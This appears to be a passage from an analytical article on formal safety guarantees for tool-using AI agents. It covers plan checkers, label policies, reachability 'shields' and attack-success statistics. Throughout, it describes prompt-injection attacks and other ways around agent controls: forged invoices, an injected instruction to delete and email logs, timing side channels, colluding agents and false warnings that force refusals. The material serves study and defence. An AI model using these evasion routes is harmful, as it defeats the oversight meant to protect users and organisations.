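Names that start with `@` are variables, like cells in a spreadsheet. The pattern in braces picks out one field and ignores the rest. After the program runs, the reader can switch from the formulas to their values, and the display crosses out the branch that did not apply. To process a list of messages, the author applies the same operation to the whole list, without writing a loop.

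Meijer wants anyone who can write basic Excel formulas to be able to understand a Universalis program, but he reports no test of whether they can. A program can include conditions that must hold before or after it runs, much like the Excel rules that reject invalid entries. If the supplier program required a positive amount as a postcondition, the check would detect a negative amount only after the program had added it to the ledger.

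Universalis has since become part of Meijer's work on agents. At a 2026 conference, he linked it to Automind, the system that runs Universalis programs. AI Engineer describes Automind as built around checked execution plans.

Automind stores the prose above as a list of comments and formulas, which other software can display in whatever form suits the reader. Meijer's email plan is also a single JSON file, which software can show as an explanation or compile into code. Skele-Code likewise keeps one file behind its canvas and descriptions. The office manager could therefore read the supplier plan as prose, while accounting sees it as a diagram and a checker analyses the stored steps.

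This works only if every form describes the same program. In Universalis, the model writes the comments as well as the formulas, so a comment could read "over 1,000 euros" beside a formula that tests for 10,000. In one of Meijer's own examples, which converts files, the folder is `@dir` in the question, `@src` in the explanation and `@directory` in the formula.

His file-deletion plan has a more dangerous mismatch. The step's description names only the two files the user wants to delete, but its call deletes every text file in the folder. A user who read only the description would approve that loss. Software can avoid this by ignoring the model's description and writing its own from the call, such as "Delete every file whose name ends in .txt."

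## What the guarantees assume and what they leave out

An accurate description tells the user what a step will do, but the step can still be a mistake. Similarly, each formal guarantee covers one property of an agent's behaviour, and an agent with that property can still pay the wrong person or delete the wrong files.

### Six properties a designer can claim

| Property | Main assumption | A harmful run that still satisfies it |
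|---|---|---|
| Every call is well formed | software enforces the schema | the agent emails Michelle's messages to a stranger, whose address is a valid string |
| No action outside the catalogue | the agent has no other way to act, and each tool does only what its definition states | an agent whose only tool is `forward_invoice` forwards a forged invoice |
| Tool output cannot change the steps | the planner reads no tool output, and the interpreter follows the plan | the agent pays the altered account number on Acme's invoice |
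| No forbidden flow | the labels and policies are correct | the agent pays a trusted supplier's bill twice |
| The agent obeys a stated rule | the checker sees every relevant call and has the facts that the rule needs | a rule requires two files to disappear, and the agent deletes every other text file as well |
| The result is correct | someone has specified the whole result, including what must stay unchanged | an employee asks the agent to send the customer list to a rival firm, and it sends exactly that list |

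A designer has to establish each property separately. SPA without its label checks fixes the steps but lets a false account number through. FIDES can block that number, but its planner reads some tool results and uses them to choose its next steps.

Correctness is the hardest property to guarantee, because few tasks come with a complete specification. Odersky and colleagues list it among TACIT's non-goals. The compiler can keep a program from leaking a secret report, but the program may still summarise the report badly.

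### Proofs, probability bounds and benchmark scores

A proof covers every input, including attacks nobody has thought of, provided the real system matches the mathematical description. A probability bound limits how often failures occur, provided future runs resemble the data behind the bound. A benchmark score counts the failures in a fixed set of test runs.

The two attacks that succeeded against the agent built by Garby and colleagues did not contradict their theorem, because the theorem does not guarantee that endorsed data is trustworthy.

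Conversely, a score of zero does not rule out failures. If each attack succeeds with probability $p$ and the runs are independent, the chance of seeing no success in $n$ runs is $(1-p)^n$. Setting this to 0.05 gives an upper 95% bound on $p$:

$$p_{\max} = 1 - 0.05^{1/n} \approx \frac{3}{n}.$$

SPA's zero successes in 949 attacked runs therefore give a bound of about 0.3%, and TACIT's zero leaks in 131 trials give about 2.3%.

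These bounds are too optimistic because the runs were not independent. SPA's 949 runs came from pairing 97 user tasks with attackers' goals, so about ten runs share each task, and every run used the same model and style of attack. If the plan for a task has a weakness, several attacks on that task may succeed, as four did when SPA ran without label checks.

In the extreme case, all runs on the same task succeed or fail together. SPA's experiment would then contain only 97 independent results, and its bound would rise to about 3%. TACIT's trials would contain only 23, one for each of the 12 tasks and 11 malicious requests, and its bound would be about 12%. The appropriate figures probably lie between these extremes and the simple bounds.

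Refusals also make SPA's score harder to interpret. A run that the label checks refuse is safe, but it provides no evidence about what happens when SPA carries out a plan. Only about 37% of runs reached execution. If that share also holds under attack, about 350 attacked runs tested execution, and zero successful attacks among them would give an upper bound of about 0.9% on the attack success rate.

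With each model, Garby and colleagues' agent resisted all 291 runs of attacks that needed a tool call outside the user's task. The runs were 97 cases repeated three times each, so the researchers based their 95% confidence interval on the 97 cases, which puts the lower bound for the resistance rate at 96.2%. Treating all 291 runs as independent would have raised that bound to about 98.7%.

### Reachability certificates

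A probability bound can also cover untested models. *Controller-Agnostic Runtime Safety Certificates for Tool-Using AI Agents via Data-Driven Robust Reachability* (Baheri and Wei, 2026) bounds the probability that an agent does something irreversible during a task. The paper's software, called a shield, sits between the model and its tools.

An engineer chooses a few yes-or-no facts, such as whether the agent is in a protected folder, whether it can write files and whether it has received confirmation. Each combination of answers is a state, and some states are unsafe, such as one where the agent has deleted production data. For each state, the shield lists the types of tool call the agent may make. The list always includes HALT, which hands the task to a person.

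Let $D(s)$ be the calls permitted in state $s$, and let $P(s' \mid s,a)$ be the probability that call $a$ leads from $s$ to $s'$. The highest possible chance of reaching an unsafe state within $k$ calls is

$$V_k(s) = \max_{a \in D(s)} \sum_{s'} P(s' \mid s,a)\, V_{k-1}(s').$$

$V$ is always 1 in an unsafe state and 0 after HALT. In every other state, $V_0$ is 0 because the agent has no calls left. Taking the maximum assumes that the model always makes the most dangerous permitted call, so the result holds for any model behind the shield.

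Nobody knows the probabilities exactly, so Baheri and Wei estimate them from logs of earlier runs. For each state and call, they find the range of probabilities that fits the logs and use the worst values in that range. If the logs contain too few examples, the calculation allows for any outcome the engineer has listed as possible, so the logs need not contain any accidents. An algorithm then removes permitted calls until the calculated risk is within a chosen limit.

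Logged calls are not independent either, because each result influences what the agent does next. *A Three-Layer Probabilistic Assume-Guarantee Architecture Is Structurally Required* (2026), another proposal for probabilistic guarantees, lists estimation from such logs as an open problem, and its bounds need new estimates whenever the model changes. Baheri and Wei handle the dependence by choosing how many examples of each call to use before they look at the logs and applying an inequality that does not require independence. Their method needs no new estimates when the model changes, because its probabilities describe how the tools respond rather than how the model behaves.

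The first test of the method used a simulated grid, where the true probabilities were known. One shield had a certified risk of 7.2% and a true worst-case risk of 0.9%. Over 200 fresh sets of logs, the true risk never exceeded the certified risk.

Baheri and Wei then tested a shield in a simulated file system. They used a scripted agent and three sizes of Qwen2.5, an older family of open models, with each size run at two randomness settings. Each of the seven versions ran 150 times, and in 39 of those runs a file contained an instruction to delete the production logs and email them out. The worst version reached an unsafe state in 84.7% of runs without the shield, but no version did in 1,050 runs with it. They calculate an upper bound of 0.29% on the average unsafe rate, but all the runs used the same simulated system and the same kind of attack.

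The shield's effect on task completion depended on the model. With randomness off, the largest model completed 55.3% of tasks with or without the shield. The middle-sized model improved from 3.3% to 38.7%, because when the shield refused a call, the model went back for a confirmation it had skipped. The smallest model kept proposing a forbidden call until the shield halted it, and it completed no tasks.

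The method's use of worst-case probabilities also mattered. Another shield treated the estimated probabilities as exact, so it assigned zero probability to accidents missing from the logs. It certified zero risk, but an adversarial program caused harm in all 200 test runs.

The certificate rests on four stated assumptions:

- The chosen facts capture everything in the agent's history that affects what happens next.
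- Unsafe states are permanent.
- The agent can always stop safely.
- Tools respond to a given call in the same way whichever model makes it.

The guarantees also assume that the engineer has listed every possible outcome of each call and that the tools keep behaving as they did in the logs. If someone later learns to forge confirmations, the old probabilities no longer apply.

Logs can disprove the assumption that the probabilities of a call's outcomes depend only on the current state and the call, but they cannot confirm it. When Baheri and Wei removed the fact recording confirmation from the state, their test detected a violation in four of the seven combinations of state and call that it could check. With that fact included, it found none. However, small effects can accumulate. If earlier history can change the probabilities of a call's outcomes by a total of $\eta$, it can add as much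 as $T\eta/2$ to the risk over $T$ calls. The largest difference measured in the file system was 0.08, which chance could explain. If it were real, it could add as much as 40 percentage points to the risk over ten calls.

A shield that permits only HALT has a certified risk of zero, but Baheri and Wei call it "safe and useless" because the agent can do nothing else.

### What every design has to trust

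The guarantees depend on someone writing the policies and labels correctly. *SPA* places the label orderings, each tool's policy and the link between a tool's name and its code in the trusted computing base, the set of components that must work correctly for the guarantee to hold. An incorrect policy can allow a harmful plan or refuse a harmless one. Girrens and Wang suggest measuring how well SPA works when labels are wrong, but have not done so.

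The guarantees also assume that each tool's code does only what it is supposed to do. SPA's containers and format checks restrict a tool that only converts files, but a payment tool needs access to the bank. If its code replaces the account number after SPA has approved the call, the money goes to the wrong account even though the plan and its labels are correct.

The checker must be sound, meaning it never approves something its rules forbid. CaMeL defines its flow rules only in its Python code, which Garby and colleagues consider hard to audit. Without a separate definition, a reviewer cannot easily tell a fault from an intended exception. Garby and colleagues avoid this problem by proving that their own interpreter matches a formal definition. SPA has no such proof, though its language is much smaller.

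Finally, the guarantees assume that the agent can reach the outside world only through the interface. If it has another route, restricting its tool calls does not contain it. Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (July 2026) describes how Claude models broke into the systems of three real organisations during evaluations that a misconfiguration had left connected to the internet.

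### Timing and termination

An agent can reveal a secret without sending it anywhere. Odersky and colleagues give the example of a function that takes longer to process hidden text when the text has a certain property. Anyone who can time the function learns one bit of the secret. TACIT does not prevent this, because its compiler checks which capabilities a function uses but not how long it takes.

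Whether a program finishes can also reveal one bit of information, and CaMeL's retry loop lets an attacker repeat the test. An eight-digit account number contains about 27 bits, so 27 well-chosen yes-or-no tests would be enough to recover it.

*PerMIT* (2026) describes a machine-checked design for an agent's long-term memory. Its interface returns no clock reading or step count, so timing cannot affect the protected part of the agent through the interface. But the proofs do not cover an outsider who measures how long the system takes to respond. They also assume unlimited storage. In a real system, an attacker who controls how much text the system stores could use "storage full" errors as a signal.

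### False answers and harmful requests

If a quarantined model misreads a bill for 9,900 euros as 990, its answer still has the right type and label. A rule that lets the user see untrusted text will also let them see this figure. The user may then pay the wrong amount through a banking website, where the agent's checks do not apply.

Most of the designs also assume that the user means well. TACIT is an exception, but only for secrets. Rules written by someone other than the user, such as a Cedar rule that limits payments to $500, can help. But an employee who is allowed to pay suppliers could still ask for a $400 payment to a company they secretly own. The agent would be following both its instructions and its policy, so the employer would need audits or a second approver to catch the fraud.

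### Agents that each follow their own rules

Suppose a company has two agents. A mail agent can read Michelle's messages but can write only to colleagues and other agents. A publicity agent can email anyone but cannot open a mailbox. The mail agent could pass a private message to the publicity agent, which could then send it to a journalist. The message would have left the company even though each agent obeyed its own rule.

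*Safety is Non-Compositional* (2026) proves a general version of this problem. Two agents that cannot reach a forbidden capability on their own may reach it together if it requires one capability from each. The smallest example has three capabilities, the forbidden one and one held by each agent. A diagram that only links capabilities in pairs cannot show this danger, because neither agent's capability is enough by itself.

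Private information can leak in the same way. *The Sum Leaks More Than Its Parts* (2025) describes an attacker who asks several agents for details that seem harmless, such as a location, a job role or an ID number, and combines the answers to identify someone. Responsibility also becomes harder to assign. *Compliant with Local Controls, Collectively Discriminatory* (2026) includes cases from AI in finance where the joint outcome can't be traced to any one component and no owner can explain or answer for it.

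The theorem shows that checking two agents separately does not establish that they are safe together. It does not show that combinations of safe agents are usually dangerous. Checking both as one system can work. For example, if Michelle's message kept its private label, a check on the publicity agent's email tool could block the message. ELBA's compiler similarly checks subagents as part of the surrounding program.

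The guarantees are harder to enforce when the agents have different owners. *Pandora's Toolbox Or Why Agent Safety Cannot Be Verified* (2026) explains that a monitor able to read every agent's context would reduce much of the problem to the single-agent case, but that agents may belong to different parties with their own safety mechanisms. The receiving company would have to understand the sender's labels and agree to enforce them.

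### Forcing an agent to stop

An attacker can also exploit an agent that stops when in doubt by giving it false reasons to doubt. Xiao (2026), in *When Safety Becomes an Attack Surface*, put false risk warnings into documents and other untrusted content that agents read while doing legitimate tasks. The attacker gained no data or money, but the agents often refused to do the tasks.

The test used 51 pairs of tasks, with the false warning present in one task of each pair and absent in the other. The table shows how often an agent completed the task without the warning but failed with it. In one condition, the prompt also included an instruction to put caution first.

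| Model | Ordinary prompt | Prompt that puts caution first |
|---|---|---|
| DeepSeek-v4-Pro | 21.6% | 64.7% |
| GPT-5.4 | 27.5% | 41.2% |
| Gemini 3 Flash | 9.8% | 86.3% |

Gemini completed 96% of tasks without a warning under either prompt, so a test without attackers would not have shown the effect. GPT-5.4's result is less clear because the cautious prompt also reduced its success on ordinary tasks from 88% to 71%. Each task ran only once in each condition.

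Xiao then labelled content by how far its source could be trusted and told the agents to check any warning against an official record or the underlying document. On 15 document tasks with false warnings, the three models completed between 73% and 100% with the new instructions, up from between 13% and 33% under the cautious prompt. In a set of publishing tasks, however, GPT-5.4 improved only from 31% to 38%. Xiao supplied the source labels, so the experiment did not test whether a real system could assign them reliably. Checking the official record will not help if an attacker can change it.

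In Xiao's experiment, a model decided whether to stop, but software that always stops after an error is also vulnerable. SPA ends a request if a tool returns data in the wrong format, so whoever controls that tool can block the task at will. The one exception is when a plan would show the user a forbidden value, in which case SPA hides that value and shows the rest. *PerMIT* likewise treats availability as an unresolved risk, because an attacker who can trigger rejections may prevent the system from promoting stored entries.

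Stopping can also cause harm. If an agent cancels a flight and then has to stop before booking the replacement, the traveller has no flight. Baheri and Wei's method assumes that HALT is always safe, so this outcome would not count as harm under their certificate unless the engineer had defined it as an unsafe state.

Letting the agent try again can reduce unnecessary stops. When Baheri and Wei's shield blocked a forbidden call from a Qwen model, the model could propose another, and the run halted only after four refusals in a row. The shield's certificate still holds after a refusal because every call that runs must be on the permitted list. However, the certificate covers only irreversible harm, not what an attacker could learn from repeated refusals, a risk SPA avoids by allowing no second attempt.
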